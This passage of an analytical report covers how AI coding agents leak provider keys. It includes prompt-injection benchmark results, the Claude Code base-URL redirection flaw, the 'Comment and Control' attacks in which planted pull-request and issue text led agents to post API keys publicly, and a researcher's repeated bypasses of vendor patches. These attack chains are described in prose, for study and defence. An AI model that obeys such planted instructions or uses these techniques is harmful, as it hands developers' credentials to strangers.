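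Anthropic recommends treating the results as a measurement of the models, not of a complete deployment, because the evaluation left out the safeguards in the two companies' own browser extensions. It also notes that OpenAI had released a new version of Auto-review about a week before the announcement, which could change OpenAI's figures.

### Why the rates do not form a trend

The two studies differed in almost every way, so the drop in headline figures, from up to 84 percent in September 2025 to zero in August 2026, doesn't show that the problem is almost solved. Newer models may well resist planted commands better, but these studies can't show by how much.

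The two studies have no combination of agent and model in common. Liu and colleagues tested Cursor and Copilot with the models of mid-2025, while Trajectory Labs tested Claude Code and Codex with models released later. The planted text also reached the agents by different routes. In the AIShellJack tests, it was in a rules file that the user had told the agent to follow, so even an agent that knew where the text came from might have obeyed it. Trajectory Labs planted its attacks in content that the agent encountered through its tools and browser and had no reason to obey.

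AIShellJack and Trajectory Labs also scored agents differently. One AIShellJack payload is an instruction to list all environment variables, and an agent that printed the list failed the test. Of the 314 payloads, 56 only gather information about the machine in this way, and Cursor in Auto carried out 91 percent of them. Under Trajectory Labs' definition, an agent that printed the list and did nothing else would have passed.

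Trajectory Labs used attacks that had been optimised against Claude Opus 4.7, an older model that is not in the published results. An attacker targeting Opus 5 in auto mode would tune the attack against that combination, which nobody did in this evaluation. The effect on the comparison between companies is harder to predict. Attacks tuned on one Claude model might carry over to its successors more easily than to GPT-5.6 Sol, but Anthropic might also have trained those successors to resist whatever worked on Opus 4.7.

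Tuning attacks to a particular defense can make them far more successful. Maloyan and Namiot collect figures for six systems that try to detect prompt injection. Each was originally reported to let through less than 12 percent of attacks. When researchers adapted their attacks to each system, between 78 and 93 percent got through.

Anthropic also paid for the later test and published it to justify a change to its own product. The design's strength is that Anthropic did not see the scenarios in advance, so it could not prepare for them. But a company that commissions a test still decides whether to publish the results and which competitor to include.

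In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, Willison (2026), a software developer who has written about prompt injection since 2022, asks for more independent confirmation. He accepts that auto mode is better than asking people to approve everything, but worries about a package whose instructions tell the agent to fetch a malicious helper program before running the tests. He doubts that any version of auto mode could stop this. His example closely resembles the 0DIN repository, where each step also looked like ordinary setup.

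Three weeks later, the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported an attack on Opus 5 in auto mode that he says works 80 percent of the time. Willison (2026), in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, agrees with a reader's objection that this was not a classic prompt injection, because the model never followed an instruction from the attacker. Rehberger's figure therefore measures a danger that the Trajectory Labs evaluation did not cover, and it doesn't contradict that evaluation's result of zero.

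Other results from 2026 are also inconsistent with a steady decline. *IssueTrojanBench* (Vaughan, 2026) summarises a benchmark from July, the same month as the versions Trajectory Labs tested. In 4,176 runs, three widely used coding agents encountered malicious instructions planted in GitHub issues, the pages where users report bugs. Vaughan reports that 66.5 percent of the malicious issues got past every safeguard and that the agents' harnesses blocked none of them, so any resistance came from the models.

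*SKILLSHIELD* (Wu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) found that six models without added defences complied with 46 to 80 percent of requests to run malicious code. The requests came directly from the user, so a model could comply without mistaking where the request came from. Combining these rates with those for planted commands would mix willingness to help a malicious user with failure to protect an honest one.

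To measure a trend, researchers would have to run the same test on each new generation of agents. The UK AI Security Institute's *CodeIPI* (2026) is an open test that could be used this way. It has 35 coding tasks with planted instructions and 10 without, to check whether an agent raises false alarms. The agent works in a container that has no outside network and has fake secrets in environment variables and a file. Results from a fixed version would be comparable from year to year, at least until developers began to train their models on the public tasks.

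### What a low rate means over many attempts

Even a low success rate can be serious for an agent that often encounters planted commands. Suppose that each attempt has a 1 percent chance of success and that the attempts are independent, so that the result of one gives no information about the next. The agent resists any single attempt with probability 0.99, and it resists 100 attempts in a row with probability 0.99 multiplied by itself 100 times, which is about 0.37. The chance that at least one attempt succeeds is therefore

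1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 0.63, or about 63 percent.

A single success may be enough, because a thief can use a stolen provider key until its owner revokes it.

Assuming that attempts are independent leaves out the similarities between them. If one planted text in every hundred always worked against a certain agent and the others never did, a text picked at random would have a 1 percent chance of working. An agent that met 100 texts picked separately at random would have about a 63 percent chance of obeying at least one. But if it met the same randomly picked text 100 times, the chance would be only 1 percent, since a text that failed once would fail every time.

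Because of the same resemblance, one effective text can harm many developers at once. If 100 developers use this agent and open the same malicious repository, either all of them lose their keys or none do, although the average number of thefts is the same as if the attempts were independent.

The rate also changes over time. An attacker who sees an attempt fail can rewrite the text and try again, as the results for adapted attacks suggest. A vendor that learns of a successful text can train its model or classifier to recognise it, and the text is then less likely to work against anyone who installs the update. Within one session, an earlier planted command also remains in the prompt and may make the model more or less suspicious of the next one.

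The 100 in the example are planted commands, not pages read or commands run. An agent may read thousands of files that contain no attack. None of these experiments measured how often agents encounter planted commands in ordinary work, so the 63 percent can't be converted into a risk per month or per project.

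## The Claude Code base URL flaw: a key sent to the wrong server

A coding agent can leak its provider key even if the model never obeys a planted command like those in the experiments above, because the harness sends the key with every model request. In October 2025, researchers at the security company Check Point reported that a file in a repository could make Claude Code send those requests, including the key, to an attacker's server. Claude Code sent the key as soon as a developer started it in the project folder.

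### What a base URL does

A base URL is the first part of the web address where the harness sends model requests. For Claude Code it is normally `https://api.anthropic.com`, and the harness adds a path such as `/v1/messages`. Users can change the base URL with the environment variable `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, which Anthropic provides for routing requests through a proxy or gateway. A company might use it to route all its developers' requests through its own server.

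The harness sends the key in a header, a labelled line ahead of the request's content, to whichever server the base URL points to. Whoever sets the base URL therefore decides who receives the key. Encryption hides the key from anyone intercepting the request, but the receiving server decrypts the request and can read the key. That server can also forward the request to Anthropic and return the real answer, so the user sees a normal session.

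### How opening a project sent out the key

Claude Code reads a project's settings, which can include environment variables, from `.claude/settings.json` in the repository. Teams commit this file so that everyone who clones the project gets the same settings. Anyone who can commit to the repository can change the file.

Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026) found the flaw while studying what the file could control, as they describe in *Caught in the Hook*. They used the base URL to send Claude Code's traffic through a program on their own computer that displays web requests. Several requests appeared before they had answered the trust dialog, which asks whether the user trusts the folder. The requests seemed to contain recent commit messages and file names from the repository, and every one included their full API key in readable form.

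An attack would have gone as follows:

1. The attacker commits a settings file that names their own server as the base URL.
2. A developer clones the repository and starts Claude Code in the folder.
3. Claude Code reads the file and adopts the address.
4. Claude Code sends its start-up requests to that address with the developer's key.
5. The developer answers the trust dialog. Refusing at this point doesn't bring the key back.

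An attacker could publish a useful-looking project with such a file, or add the file to a pull request that also contains real improvements. Donenfeld and Vanunu argue that reviewers often miss such changes because they regard configuration files as metadata and read them less carefully than code.

The same researchers had earlier found CVE-2025-59536, a related flaw that let a repository's settings make Claude Code run shell commands before the user answered the trust dialog. Anthropic fixed it in September 2025, about five weeks before Check Point reported the base URL flaw.

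### Why checking commands could not have helped

In the 0DIN test, the attacker needed Claude Code to request the setup command, but the base URL attack did not depend on any decision by the model. Ordinary code in the harness wrote the start-up requests, looked up the address and attached the key, so the key would have leaked even if the model had resisted every planted instruction.

The attack did not need a shell command either, apart from the one the developer used to start Claude Code. Guard rules, permission prompts and classifiers had nothing to check, because they act on the model's tool calls and the attack involved none. Claude Code's sandbox would not have helped because its network limits apply to commands the agent runs, not to the harness's own requests to the model provider. A credential proxy could have limited the damage because the agent would not have held the real key.

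### Two severity scores for one flaw

Check Point reported the flaw on 28 October 2025, and Anthropic fixed it on 28 December. The flaw received its public catalogue number, CVE-2026-21852, on 21 January 2026, and Check Point published its account on 25 February. GCVE's database entry, *Claude Code Leaks Data via Malicious Environment Configuration Before Trust Confirmation* (2026), lists every version before 2.0.65 as affected. Users with automatic updates already had the fix when the entry appeared.

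The entry includes two severity scores on a scale from 0 to 10. GitHub, where Anthropic published its advisory, supplied a score of 5.3, and the US government's National Vulnerability Database gave 7.5. Both used the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which turns answers to a fixed set of questions into a number. However, they used different versions of the system and answered several questions differently:

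| | GitHub | National Vulnerability Database |
|---|---|---|
| CVSS version | 4.0 | 3.1 |
| Action needed from the user | Passive | None |
| Loss of confidentiality | Low | High |
| Unauthorised changes to data | Low | None |
| Loss of service | Low | None |
| Score | 5.3 (medium) | 7.5 (high) |

"Passive" means the victim does something ordinary without intending to help the attacker, such as starting Claude Code in a folder. Version 3.1 only distinguishes between some action and none. If the user's action counts as required, GitHub's answers produce 6.3 under version 3.1. The gap therefore comes partly from the change of version and partly from different judgments about the flaw.

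GitHub's assessment that the attack requires user action seems more accurate, because the attack fails if nobody opens the repository. But "low" is a surprising rating for the loss of a complete, working key. GitHub also recorded no effect on any system beyond the vulnerable one, even though the key gives a thief access to the victim's account on Anthropic's servers.

Other sites repeat one score or the other. Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, lists the flaw as medium in *CVE-2026-21852* (2026), while Action1, a company that sells software for installing updates, gives it 7.5 in its own *CVE-2026-21852*.

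Neither score measures whether anyone has used the flaw. When the entry appeared in January, the US agency CISA recorded no exploitation. GCVE also shows a statistical forecast from 2 October 2026 of about a 28 percent chance of exploitation in the following 30 days, higher than for 98 percent of catalogued flaws. Only people still running a version older than 2.0.65 are at risk.

### What a stolen key opened besides billing

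Donenfeld and Vanunu found that an attacker with a stolen key can reach files that other developers uploaded to the same workspace, as well as run models at the key owner's expense. Anthropic's Workspaces feature lets customers organise keys and files by team or project. Uploaded files belong to the workspace rather than to the key that uploaded them, so any key in the workspace can reach them.

The researchers tested this in a workspace they had created with two keys. Anthropic's file service does not let customers download files they have uploaded, but the researchers found an indirect way to obtain an identical copy. They consider the restriction a design choice, not a security barrier, because someone who can upload a file usually has the original. But a thief with a stolen key does not have the original and so gains from the copy.

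According to Donenfeld and Vanunu, a thief could also delete a team's files, add misleading ones, fill the 100-gigabyte storage allowance, or use up the account's credit until the service stopped. One developer's mistake could therefore affect colleagues who had never opened the malicious repository. If the team stores nothing in the workspace, though, a stolen key gives the thief little more than model use charged to the account.

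### What the repair leaves to the user

Since version 2.0.65, Claude Code has waited for the user to accept the trust dialog before sending any requests in an interactive session. If the user refuses, Claude Code closes without sending the key. If the user accepts, the project's settings file takes effect, and a base URL in it can still redirect requests.

Datadog Security Labs observed that in version 2.1.185, the project's environment settings took effect after the user trusted the folder and before the first prompt, without a second review. There are legitimate reasons to allow this, since a team may want to commit the address of its own gateway. Anthropic's documentation of these settings gives routing requests through a proxy as an example.

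The user therefore has to decide whether the repository is safe, and the dialog doesn't help much with this risk. Backslash Security's *Your Claude Code Token Might End Somewhere You Don’t Expect* (2026) points out that the dialog is about trusting the folder's code, not about sending a credential to an address specified in the folder. A developer who wants to know the address has to read the settings file before accepting. Donenfeld and Vanunu recommend this, but someone who has just cloned a project to work on it with Claude Code has a strong reason to click "yes".

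The fix also works only if the dialog appears. Crosley, a blogger, describes two further flaws that let a repository skip the dialog. Anthropic disclosed them in March and April 2026.

### Redirection after the repair

In July 2026, Backslash Security, which sells security tools, tested six versions of Claude Code, up to 2.1.220. Every version still sent the user's credential to whatever server the base URL named. The researchers could set the base URL in the shell's environment or in a repository's settings file.

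The settings file took effect without a new dialog if the developer already trusted the folder. Claude Code records trust by folder path and does not ask again when the contents change. A folder also inherits trust from any folder above it. A developer who trusted a repository months ago could pull a routine update that contains a new base URL and leak the credential at the next command. Anthropic limits this inheritance when a user starts Claude Code directly in their home directory, where trust lasts only for that session. But trust in a folder that holds all of a developer's projects would still cover each new one.

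Claude Code shows no dialog when run with the `-p` option, which scripts use to give it a prompt without opening an interactive session. Backslash Security ran it this way in a folder where it had never run before, and it sent the credential to the address in the settings file. Anthropic also documents that a project's environment settings apply at start-up with `-p`. The fix for CVE-2026-21852 therefore doesn't protect automated workflows, which often have their own keys.

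In these tests, Backslash Security captured a sign-in token from an account login at the other server, but never a provider API key. The token let its holder run models, upload files and open Claude Code sessions as the user, but not create new API keys. In two interactive runs with an API key set, Claude Code still sent the sign-in token, and the researchers could not explain why. This may be because, according to Anthropic, an API key replaces a subscription login in interactive sessions only after the user has approved the key once. Check Point's tests are therefore the direct evidence that redirected requests can carry an API key.

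Anthropic rated Backslash Security's report "Informative". According to Backslash Security, Anthropic's position is that a command-line tool that reads its shell environment is working as intended, and that an attacker who can set variables in someone's shell already controls the machine. Backslash Security agrees that this is not a vulnerability. The argument is convincing because such an attacker could read the stored credential directly or replace the Claude Code program.

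It is less convincing for a settings file, since an attacker can get a change merged into a repository without access to a developer's machine. Anthropic could reply that a trusted repository can already run code on the machine, so a redirected key adds little danger. But a developer may trust a folder to have Claude Code explain it, without meaning to run anything in it. Backslash Security asked Anthropic specifically about trust that is never rechecked and had not published an answer by 2 August.

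The company proposes that Claude Code get the user's approval before sending a credential to any address other than the default, and show the address in the approval prompt. An automated job has no user present to approve the request, so Claude Code would have to withhold the credential or rely on an approval stored outside the repository.

A simpler option would be for Claude Code to ignore the base URL in project settings. It already ignores other variables that a repository should not control, including, since version 2.1.282, the addresses to which it sends usage data. Anthropic's published list of these variables does not include `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, although the list may be incomplete. If Claude Code ignored the base URL, teams could no longer share a gateway address through the repository.

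Setting the correct address in the shell doesn't protect developers, because a project's settings file overrides it. An organisation can set the address in managed settings, which are deployed by an administrator and override the project's file. For everyone else, Backslash Security advises reviewing changes to `.claude/settings.json` as carefully as executable code, and signing in again after any suspected exposure, since a redirected request leaves no sign on the screen.

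## GitHub workflows that posted provider keys in public comments

In April 2026, the security researcher Aonan Guan described leaks that, unlike the base URL attack, needed no server to receive the stolen key. The coding agents posted credentials on GitHub, where the attacker could read them. Guan demonstrated the leaks in Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review, Google's Gemini CLI Action and GitHub's Copilot Agent, with help from Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University.

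### How a stranger can start an agent

GitHub Actions is a service that automates routine work on a repository. A workflow file in the repository names an event, such as someone opening an issue or a pull request (a proposed change to the code), and lists the steps to run when it occurs. GitHub then starts a hosted machine, called a runner, to carry them out.

Developers first used workflows for fixed jobs such as running tests. Microsoft (2026) explains that an AI agent in a workflow instead interprets ordinary language and decides what to do next. For example, a review agent reads each pull request's code changes, title, description and comments, then posts its findings.

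Anthropic's *Claude Code Security Review*, the guide to its review tool, includes a sample workflow that runs on every pull request. The runner downloads the proposed code and starts the agent with a provider API key from the repository's secrets, which GitHub stores encrypted and supplies to jobs. The workflow also lets the job comment on the pull request, using a repository token that GitHub creates for each job and that expires when the job ends. According to Microsoft, a runner may also hold cloud credentials and tokens for publishing packages, depending on the setup.

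No one is present to answer permission prompts, so whoever sets up the workflow has to decide in advance what the agent may do. A stranger can also start the agent by opening an issue, whereas in the 0DIN test a developer had to open the malicious repository. If the agent ignores the planted text, the stranger can open another issue with different wording.

Someone without write access to a repository usually opens pull requests from a fork, which is their own copy of it. By default, GitHub withholds secrets from workflows started by a fork's pull request, so the agent in Anthropic's sample workflow would have no key and could not call the model. However, Guan notes that some repositories use a different trigger that does supply secrets. The restriction also doesn't apply to workflows started by issues, which anyone with a GitHub account can normally open in a public repository.

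### Three leaks with the same chain

In *Comment and Control* (Guan, 2026), Guan names the attack after "command and control", the channel through which an attacker directs hijacked computers. All three versions followed the same steps:

1. A stranger writes instructions in a pull request or issue, and the workflow adds them to the agent's prompt.
2. The agent follows the instructions and collects credentials from the runner.
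3. The agent's output, including the credentials, appears on GitHub.

Claude Code Security Review copied the title of a pull request into the prompt. Guan put instructions for Claude to run commands in a title. The harness did not restrict Claude's tools and passed on all the runner's environment variables, so the commands could print the Anthropic API key and the repository token. Claude reported this output as a security finding, and the workflow posted it as a comment on the pull request.

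The output also appeared in the job's log. Guan considers this a stealthier way to collect the key because maintainers rarely read logs. The attacker could do so without leaving a trace in the conversation, although the strange title would still be visible.

Gemini CLI Action, which handles GitHub issues, included each issue's title, text and comments in its prompt. The researchers put instructions in an issue's title, then added comments that pushed the agent further. Techzine's *AI agents on GitHub leak API keys via prompt injection* says the attack involved a fake section of instructions. Gemini posted its own provider API key in a public comment.

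The attack on Copilot Agent required the victim, a maintainer, to assign an issue to Copilot, which then writes code and opens a pull request. Guan hid instructions in a part of the issue that GitHub doesn't display, so the maintainer saw only a harmless request for debugging. Copilot saved the runner's credentials in a file and added the file to its pull request. Copilot's environment filter, secret scanner and network firewall did not stop the leak.

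| | Claude Code Security Review | Gemini CLI Action | Copilot Agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Planted text | Pull request title | Issue title and comments | Hidden part of an issue |
| What starts the agent | A new pull request | A new issue or comment | A maintainer assigns the issue |
| Where the output appeared | Comment and job log | Comment | File in a pull request |
| What leaked | Anthropic API key and repository token | Gemini API key | Four GitHub and Copilot credentials |
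| Vendor's assessment | 9.4 out of 10, critical | No published score | Known architectural limitation |
| Bounty | $100 | $1,337 | $500 |

Guan shows that each attack can work but gives no success rates, so his results don't show which agent best resists planted instructions. They also don't show how many repositories strangers could have attacked, which depends on how each repository starts its workflows and supplies secrets.

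Anyone can read a key in a public comment, not just the person who planted the instructions. Criminals already search GitHub for exposed keys, so deleting the comment isn't enough and the owner has to revoke the key.

### The vendors' responses

Anthropic first scored the flaw 9.3 on the CVSS severity scale and later 9.4. It told Guan that the tool "is not designed to be hardened against prompt injection". It then blocked one program, which lists running processes, and added security advice to the documentation. Guan objects that other commands can read the same credentials. He recommends that Anthropic allow only the tools a security review needs, instead of blocking dangerous ones one by one.

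In a later update to SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection*, Guan said the attack on Claude should still work in principle with different text, but he had not tried to bypass the fix completely. Anthropic's guide still warns that the tool is not hardened and should review only trusted pull requests. The guide recommends a GitHub setting that requires a maintainer's approval before workflows run for any outside contributor.

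This warning discloses the tool's limits, but it rules out much of the tool's natural use. Anthropic's *Automate security reviews with Claude Code* presents automated reviews as a way to catch vulnerabilities before they reach production, and code from a stranger is an obvious candidate for review.

Google gave the model further instructions, which Guan calls guardrail prompts, but did not change the agent's tools. The experiments on role confusion suggest that such instructions are a weak defence.

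GitHub closed Guan's report, saying that the issue was known and that it could not reproduce the leak. Guan then used Copilot's code to show that its developers had meant to withhold these credentials from commands. GitHub reopened the report and paid him, but continued to describe the problem as a design limitation and said it was exploring further restrictions.

According to Techzine, GitHub had published plans in March for secrets with a narrower scope and a firewall for outgoing connections from Actions. A firewall can stop an agent from sending a key to an unknown server, but it is less useful against Comment and Control, because an agent that works on GitHub has to be able to post there.

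Lyons (2026) reports in *Agents hooked into GitHub can steal creds* that none of the three vendors had issued a public advisory or a CVE number for the flaws when Guan published his account. Guan told her he knew of users whose workflows were pinned to a vulnerable version. The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties, then kept quiet* also notes that people on older versions had no warning.

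Anthropic's sample workflow fetches the latest version of the review tool, so anyone who copied it would have received the fix automatically. Pinning a version blocks security fixes as well as malicious updates, so people who pin rely on advisories to know when to update.

### The Novee findings

Elad Meged, a founding engineer at Novee Security, found related weaknesses in Claude Code, Gemini CLI and Codex. Witts (2026) reports in *Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex* that Meged disclosed the weaknesses in late July and presented the full attacks at the Black Hat security conference in August. He tested the vendors' own repositories, using configurations the vendors supplied or recommended.

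Witts writes that Meged stole secrets from the vendors' repositories, but Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* names only Anthropic's. It describes an unenforced restriction in Google's agent and misplaced trust between workflow stages in OpenAI's.

Meged argues that the underlying flaw was that each harness made decisions that seemed acceptable separately but leaked secrets in combination, and that prompt injection only delivered the attacks. For example, a harness might approve a command because it only reads information, and a later step might publish the agent's output because that is the workflow's normal purpose. If the command reads a provider key, the workflow publishes the key.

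In OpenAI's case, the weakness involved a workflow whose stages shared files. An attacker's text could influence what the agent wrote in one stage, and the next stage treated that output as trusted. Codex's sandbox protected a list of paths, but the list depended on assumptions about which files needed protection.

Meged reported several rounds of findings to Anthropic. Each patch fixed the flaw he had reported but also showed him where the harness now separated safe actions from unsafe ones, and he looked for the next weakness there. By the last round, he could recover secrets without connecting to an outside server, writing anything or leaving logs. But he said Anthropic's "fixes weren't inadequate or lazy" and that its workflow ran dozens of checks.

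Meged instead criticizes how companies treat such reports. Anthropic paid him in each round, which he considers fair, but he thinks paying for individual bugs can make a problem seem solved when its cause remains. Novee has some interest in this conclusion, since he builds AI agents there for automated security testing. Still, the repeated successful attacks on the same product are good evidence for his point.

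Meged proposes checking trust again whenever a later step uses the output, as well as when the harness approves a command. This would be straightforward if the later step loaded a configuration file, because the harness could refuse any file that the agent had been able to change. It is harder for published text because the model writes from a prompt that mixes trusted and untrusted material. A strict rule against publishing anything influenced by a stranger would therefore block every review of a stranger's code.

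PointGuard AI's *GitHub Issues Turn AI Coding Agents Against CI/CD* reports no confirmed widespread exploitation at the time of the Black Hat disclosure. Underhill (2026) says in *Black Hat 2026* that a single untrusted issue could compromise an automated workflow.

### Google's change to its trust model

Google had already published an advisory on 24 April, nine days after Guan's account. The advisory, which the vulnerability database OSV reproduces as *GHSA-wpqr-6v78-jr5g* (2026), covers two flaws in Gemini CLI, the coding agent that Gemini CLI Action runs. It gives them the maximum severity score of 10.0 and credits Meged and Dan Lisichkin of Pillar Security. Corgea's *Gemini CLI* lists the advisory as CVE-2026-12537.

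When Gemini CLI ran without a user present, it automatically trusted its working folder and loaded settings and environment variables from it. If the folder contained a stranger's pull request, those settings could make the runner execute the stranger's code. Claude Code's `-p` option similarly skips the trust dialog.

The other problem was that Gemini CLI, in a mode that approves actions automatically, ignored the details of the operator's list of allowed commands. An operator who allowed only a harmless command that prints text had in practice allowed every shell command. Google recommended a strict list for workflows that handle strangers' issues, so people who followed its advice could still be exposed to prompt injection.

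Gemini CLI version 0.39.1 fixed both problems. It requires explicit trust before loading a folder's settings and enforces the command list in automatic mode. Google's earlier response to Guan had changed only the model's instructions, but this update gives operators a working limit on what the agent can run.

The update also broke some existing workflows. Google warned that workflows relying on automatic trust would no longer load their folder's settings, and that others might fail without an error until their owners revised the list of allowed commands. An operator can restore trust by setting one variable. Google tells operators who handle untrusted material to harden their workflows first, but someone in a hurry to repair a broken workflow could skip that step.

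Workflows run the latest Gemini CLI by default, so most should have received the fix. Google advises anyone who specified an older version to upgrade.

### Keeping secrets out of jobs that strangers start

A planted instruction can't reveal secrets from a job that has none. By default, GitHub doesn't pass stored secrets to workflows triggered by pull requests from forks. Projects can add protection by having a maintainer approve each outside contribution before the agent runs.

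The main drawback of requiring approval is delay. An agent needs a provider key to use its model, so removing the key from the job usually stops the agent from running. A credential proxy could authenticate the agent's requests without giving it the key, but someone has to maintain the proxy, and a stranger could still use up the project's credit. Requiring approval keeps the agent available but gives maintainers more work, particularly in popular projects that receive many contributions from strangers.

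In the Copilot attack, a maintainer read an issue and started the agent without seeing the malicious part, which GitHub's page did not display. To approve such a job safely, a maintainer would have to inspect the raw text that the agent will receive.

GMO Flatt Security found that one mode of Claude Code's general GitHub tool did not check whether a human account had triggered it, so an attacker could start workflows with untrusted text. The company's example was the workflow that sorts issues in Anthropic's Claude Code repository. That workflow put information from each issue into the prompt and gave the job a repository token.

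### Holding back the agent's output

A workflow can store the agent's output where only maintainers can read it and publish it only after someone has checked it. In the Claude and Gemini attacks, this would have kept the keys out of public comments. The project would also have to keep the output out of public logs, which makes failed jobs harder to investigate.

Contributors would then wait longer for feedback. Maintainers would have to read every report, many of them harmless, and might start approving them without much attention, as developers do with permission prompts. The measure also suits Copilot poorly because its output is a pull request, which is of little use until people can see it.

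For simple tasks, the harness can restrict what the agent publishes. Suppose an agent sorts issues by choosing exactly one of 16 labels, and the harness publishes nothing else. Each choice can reveal at most 4 bits, because 2⁴ = 16. A key of 40 random characters, each drawn from 64 possibilities, contains 40 × 6 = 240 bits, so an attacker would need at least 240 / 4 = 60 issues to extract it, even if the agent obeyed every time. Maintainers would have a good chance of noticing 60 strange issues. This restriction doesn't work for code review, because the agent has to explain problems in free text.

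This measure is not enough on its own, because Meged's last attack on Anthropic recovered secrets without an outside connection, writes or logs. He advises teams to trace where the agent's output goes after the harness approves a command, and to check whether a later step publishes it, loads it as configuration or passes it to a tool with more access.

### Short-lived tokens with narrow permissions

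The damage from a leak depends on what the credential allows and how long it works. In Anthropic's sample workflow, the repository token can read code and write comments but can't change the code, and it stops working when the job ends. It is therefore useless to an attacker who finds it in an old log, but one who sees the comment containing it while the job is running may be able to use it.

Narrow permissions also limit what a hijacked agent can do without stealing a credential. *GitHub Prompt Injection Exposed Private Repos via Issues* (Cross, 2026) describes a July 2026 demonstration by Noma Security in which agents that could read an organisation's private repositories posted the contents of those repositories in public comments. An agent that could read only the public repository would have had no private data to post.

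These limits take work to set up and maintain because someone has to determine what each workflow needs, and a job with too few permissions fails, sometimes without a clear error. Guan recommends limiting tools in the same way, arguing that an agent that reviews code may not need a shell. But without a shell, the agent can't run the project's tests to confirm a suspected bug.

Provider API keys are harder to limit because they normally work until someone revokes them. A project can create a separate key for its workflow and, where the provider allows it, set a low spending limit. With Anthropic, it can also put the key in a workspace with no files, so a thief could not reach the team's uploads. The project then has another key to track and replace, and a burst of legitimate contributions may exhaust the limit and stop the reviews.

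## Keys that agents save to disk or commit without an attacker

In the GitHub attacks, a stranger's text led the agent to publish a key. An agent can also leak a key during ordinary work, by printing it, writing it into code or running a command that contains it. The harness may then save a copy in a log or settings file that the developer never opens. Malware can find that copy, or the developer can accidentally publish it with the rest of a project.

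### How a key gets into logs and code

Many leaks start with debugging. The developer cyclopt_dimitrisk points out in *Your secrets don't need a git commit to leak* that printing every environment variable to find a configuration error also prints all the keys. A failing test may print a database address that contains the password. An agent that can run shell commands may do either without the user specifically asking.

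Skills can cause the same leak. *Credential Exfiltration Defence in Depth* (Vaughan, 2026) reports that Chen and colleagues examined 17,022 skills from one marketplace and found 520 with credential leaks. Debug messages caused 73.5 percent of the leaks, because the harness adds whatever a skill prints to the prompt. The 520 include some skills that leaked credentials deliberately.

A key in the prompt can then end up in the project's code. Docker's *Coding Agent Horror Stories* describes an agent that reads `.env` to find the name of the key it needs for a new integration. The prompt now contains the key's value as well as its name, and the model may write the value into a configuration file or a test. The program still works, so running it doesn't reveal the mistake.

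The harness may also keep its own record of the session. *Codex CLI に貼った API キーは ~/.codex/sessions と SQLite に平文で残る*, a post on the Japanese programming site Qiita, describes one user's test of a single version, Codex 0.172.0. The user, supportapp3, pasted a dummy key into a prompt, and the key appeared in plain text in a session file and a SQLite database. It was still in the database file after the user deleted the session with Codex's own command, perhaps because SQLite normally marks deleted data as free space without erasing it. A session with the `--ephemeral` option left no copy.

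### The Codex shell snapshots

In July 2026, developers reported that Codex was saving API keys that nobody had typed into a prompt or printed. In *The Shell Snapshot Blind Spot*, Vaughan traces the reports to two issues in the Codex repository, #30971 from 3 July and #32327 from 11 July. The second issue included a proposed fix.

At the start of a session, Codex saves the state of the developer's shell to a file called a shell snapshot, which it loads for each later command. OpenAI introduced snapshots in the code change *feat: POSIX unification and snapshot sessions*. Before that, the bash shells that Codex opened for commands did not load `.bashrc`, where many developers define variables and shortcuts, so commands that worked in the developer's own terminal could fail in Codex.

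To create the file, Codex runs `export -p`, which lists the name and value of every variable that the shell would pass to another program. Codex left out only `PWD` and `OLDPWD`, which hold the current and previous folders. It saved the rest under `~/.codex/shell_snapshots/`, including `OPENAI_API_KEY` if the developer had set it.

Codex already had a filter that by default removes variables with names containing words such as "KEY" from the environment it passes to commands. But separate code wrote the snapshot from the full environment without applying the filter. Vaughan says OpenAI designed the two parts independently.

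A command could therefore start without the key in its environment and still read it from the snapshot. OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* explains that the default settings let commands read files across the machine, which may include configuration files that contain API keys. The same settings block network access, so a command couldn't upload the key directly, but it could print the key into the prompt.

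Vaughan writes that the filter still prevents running commands from receiving saved keys. He also says that Codex loads the snapshot for every command, which is hard to reconcile with this because loading a list of exported variables would normally set them again. He does not report a test.

The snapshots could also contain keys that developers had deliberately kept out of files. Some developers keep a key in a password manager and have their shell fetch it at startup. Creating a snapshot runs the same startup file, which Vaughan says caused unexpected fingerprint prompts for some macOS users. If the startup file exports the key, the snapshot contains a copy of it in plain text.

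Vaughan does not list the affected versions. OpenAI's release notes show that Codex had snapshots by version 0.95.0, which set their retention period to three days. The flaw was still unfixed when Vaughan described it on 20 July 2026. Developers using a later version can search the snapshot folder for their own keys.

OpenAI had earlier changed the snapshot code, in *chore: defensive shell snapshot*, to leave out variables with invalid names so that snapshots wouldn't fail. Variables with valid names, such as `OPENAI_API_KEY`, were still saved. The fix proposed in #32327 would leave out a list of well-known secret variables and any variable whose name ends in a pattern such as `_TOKEN` or `_API_KEY`, but it would still save a key with an unusual name.

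### Commands saved in approval lists

Claude Code can save a key because of how it remembers approvals. When it asks to run a command, the user can choose not to be asked again, and Claude Code may then save the exact command in `.claude/settings.local.json` in the project folder. Christian (2026), in *37 Credentials in a JSON File I Thought Was Just Config*, gives an example with a made-up key:

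`SOME_API_KEY="sk-live-abc123" node deploy.js`

Setting the variable for one command keeps the key away from other programs, but it makes the key part of the command's text, so Claude Code saves the key with the command. Christian advises exporting the variable in the shell first and then running `node deploy.js` by itself. That keeps the key out of Claude Code's approval list, but Codex saved exported variables in its snapshots. A developer who uses both agents can't avoid both leaks just by changing how they set the variable.

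The approval list becomes public if the developer publishes the project folder with the settings file in it. Lakera's *Your AI Coding Assistant Just Shipped Your API Keys* measured how often this happens on npm, the main public registry for JavaScript packages. The security company checked about 46,500 new or updated packages. It found the file in 428 of them, and 33 of those files, in 30 packages, contained credentials.

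Another security company, Apiiro, searched public GitHub repositories for the same file. iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets* reports the results:

| | Lakera | Apiiro |
|---|---|---|
| Where it looked | npm packages | Public GitHub repositories |
| Settings files found | 428 | 104,185 |
| Files with credentials | 33 (7.7%) | 1,122 (1.1%) |

Both percentages are shares of the published settings files. The 30 packages are less than 0.1 percent of all the packages Lakera checked. The two companies may also have counted differently, since Apiiro counted "real" secrets, while Lakera's findings included passwords for test accounts.

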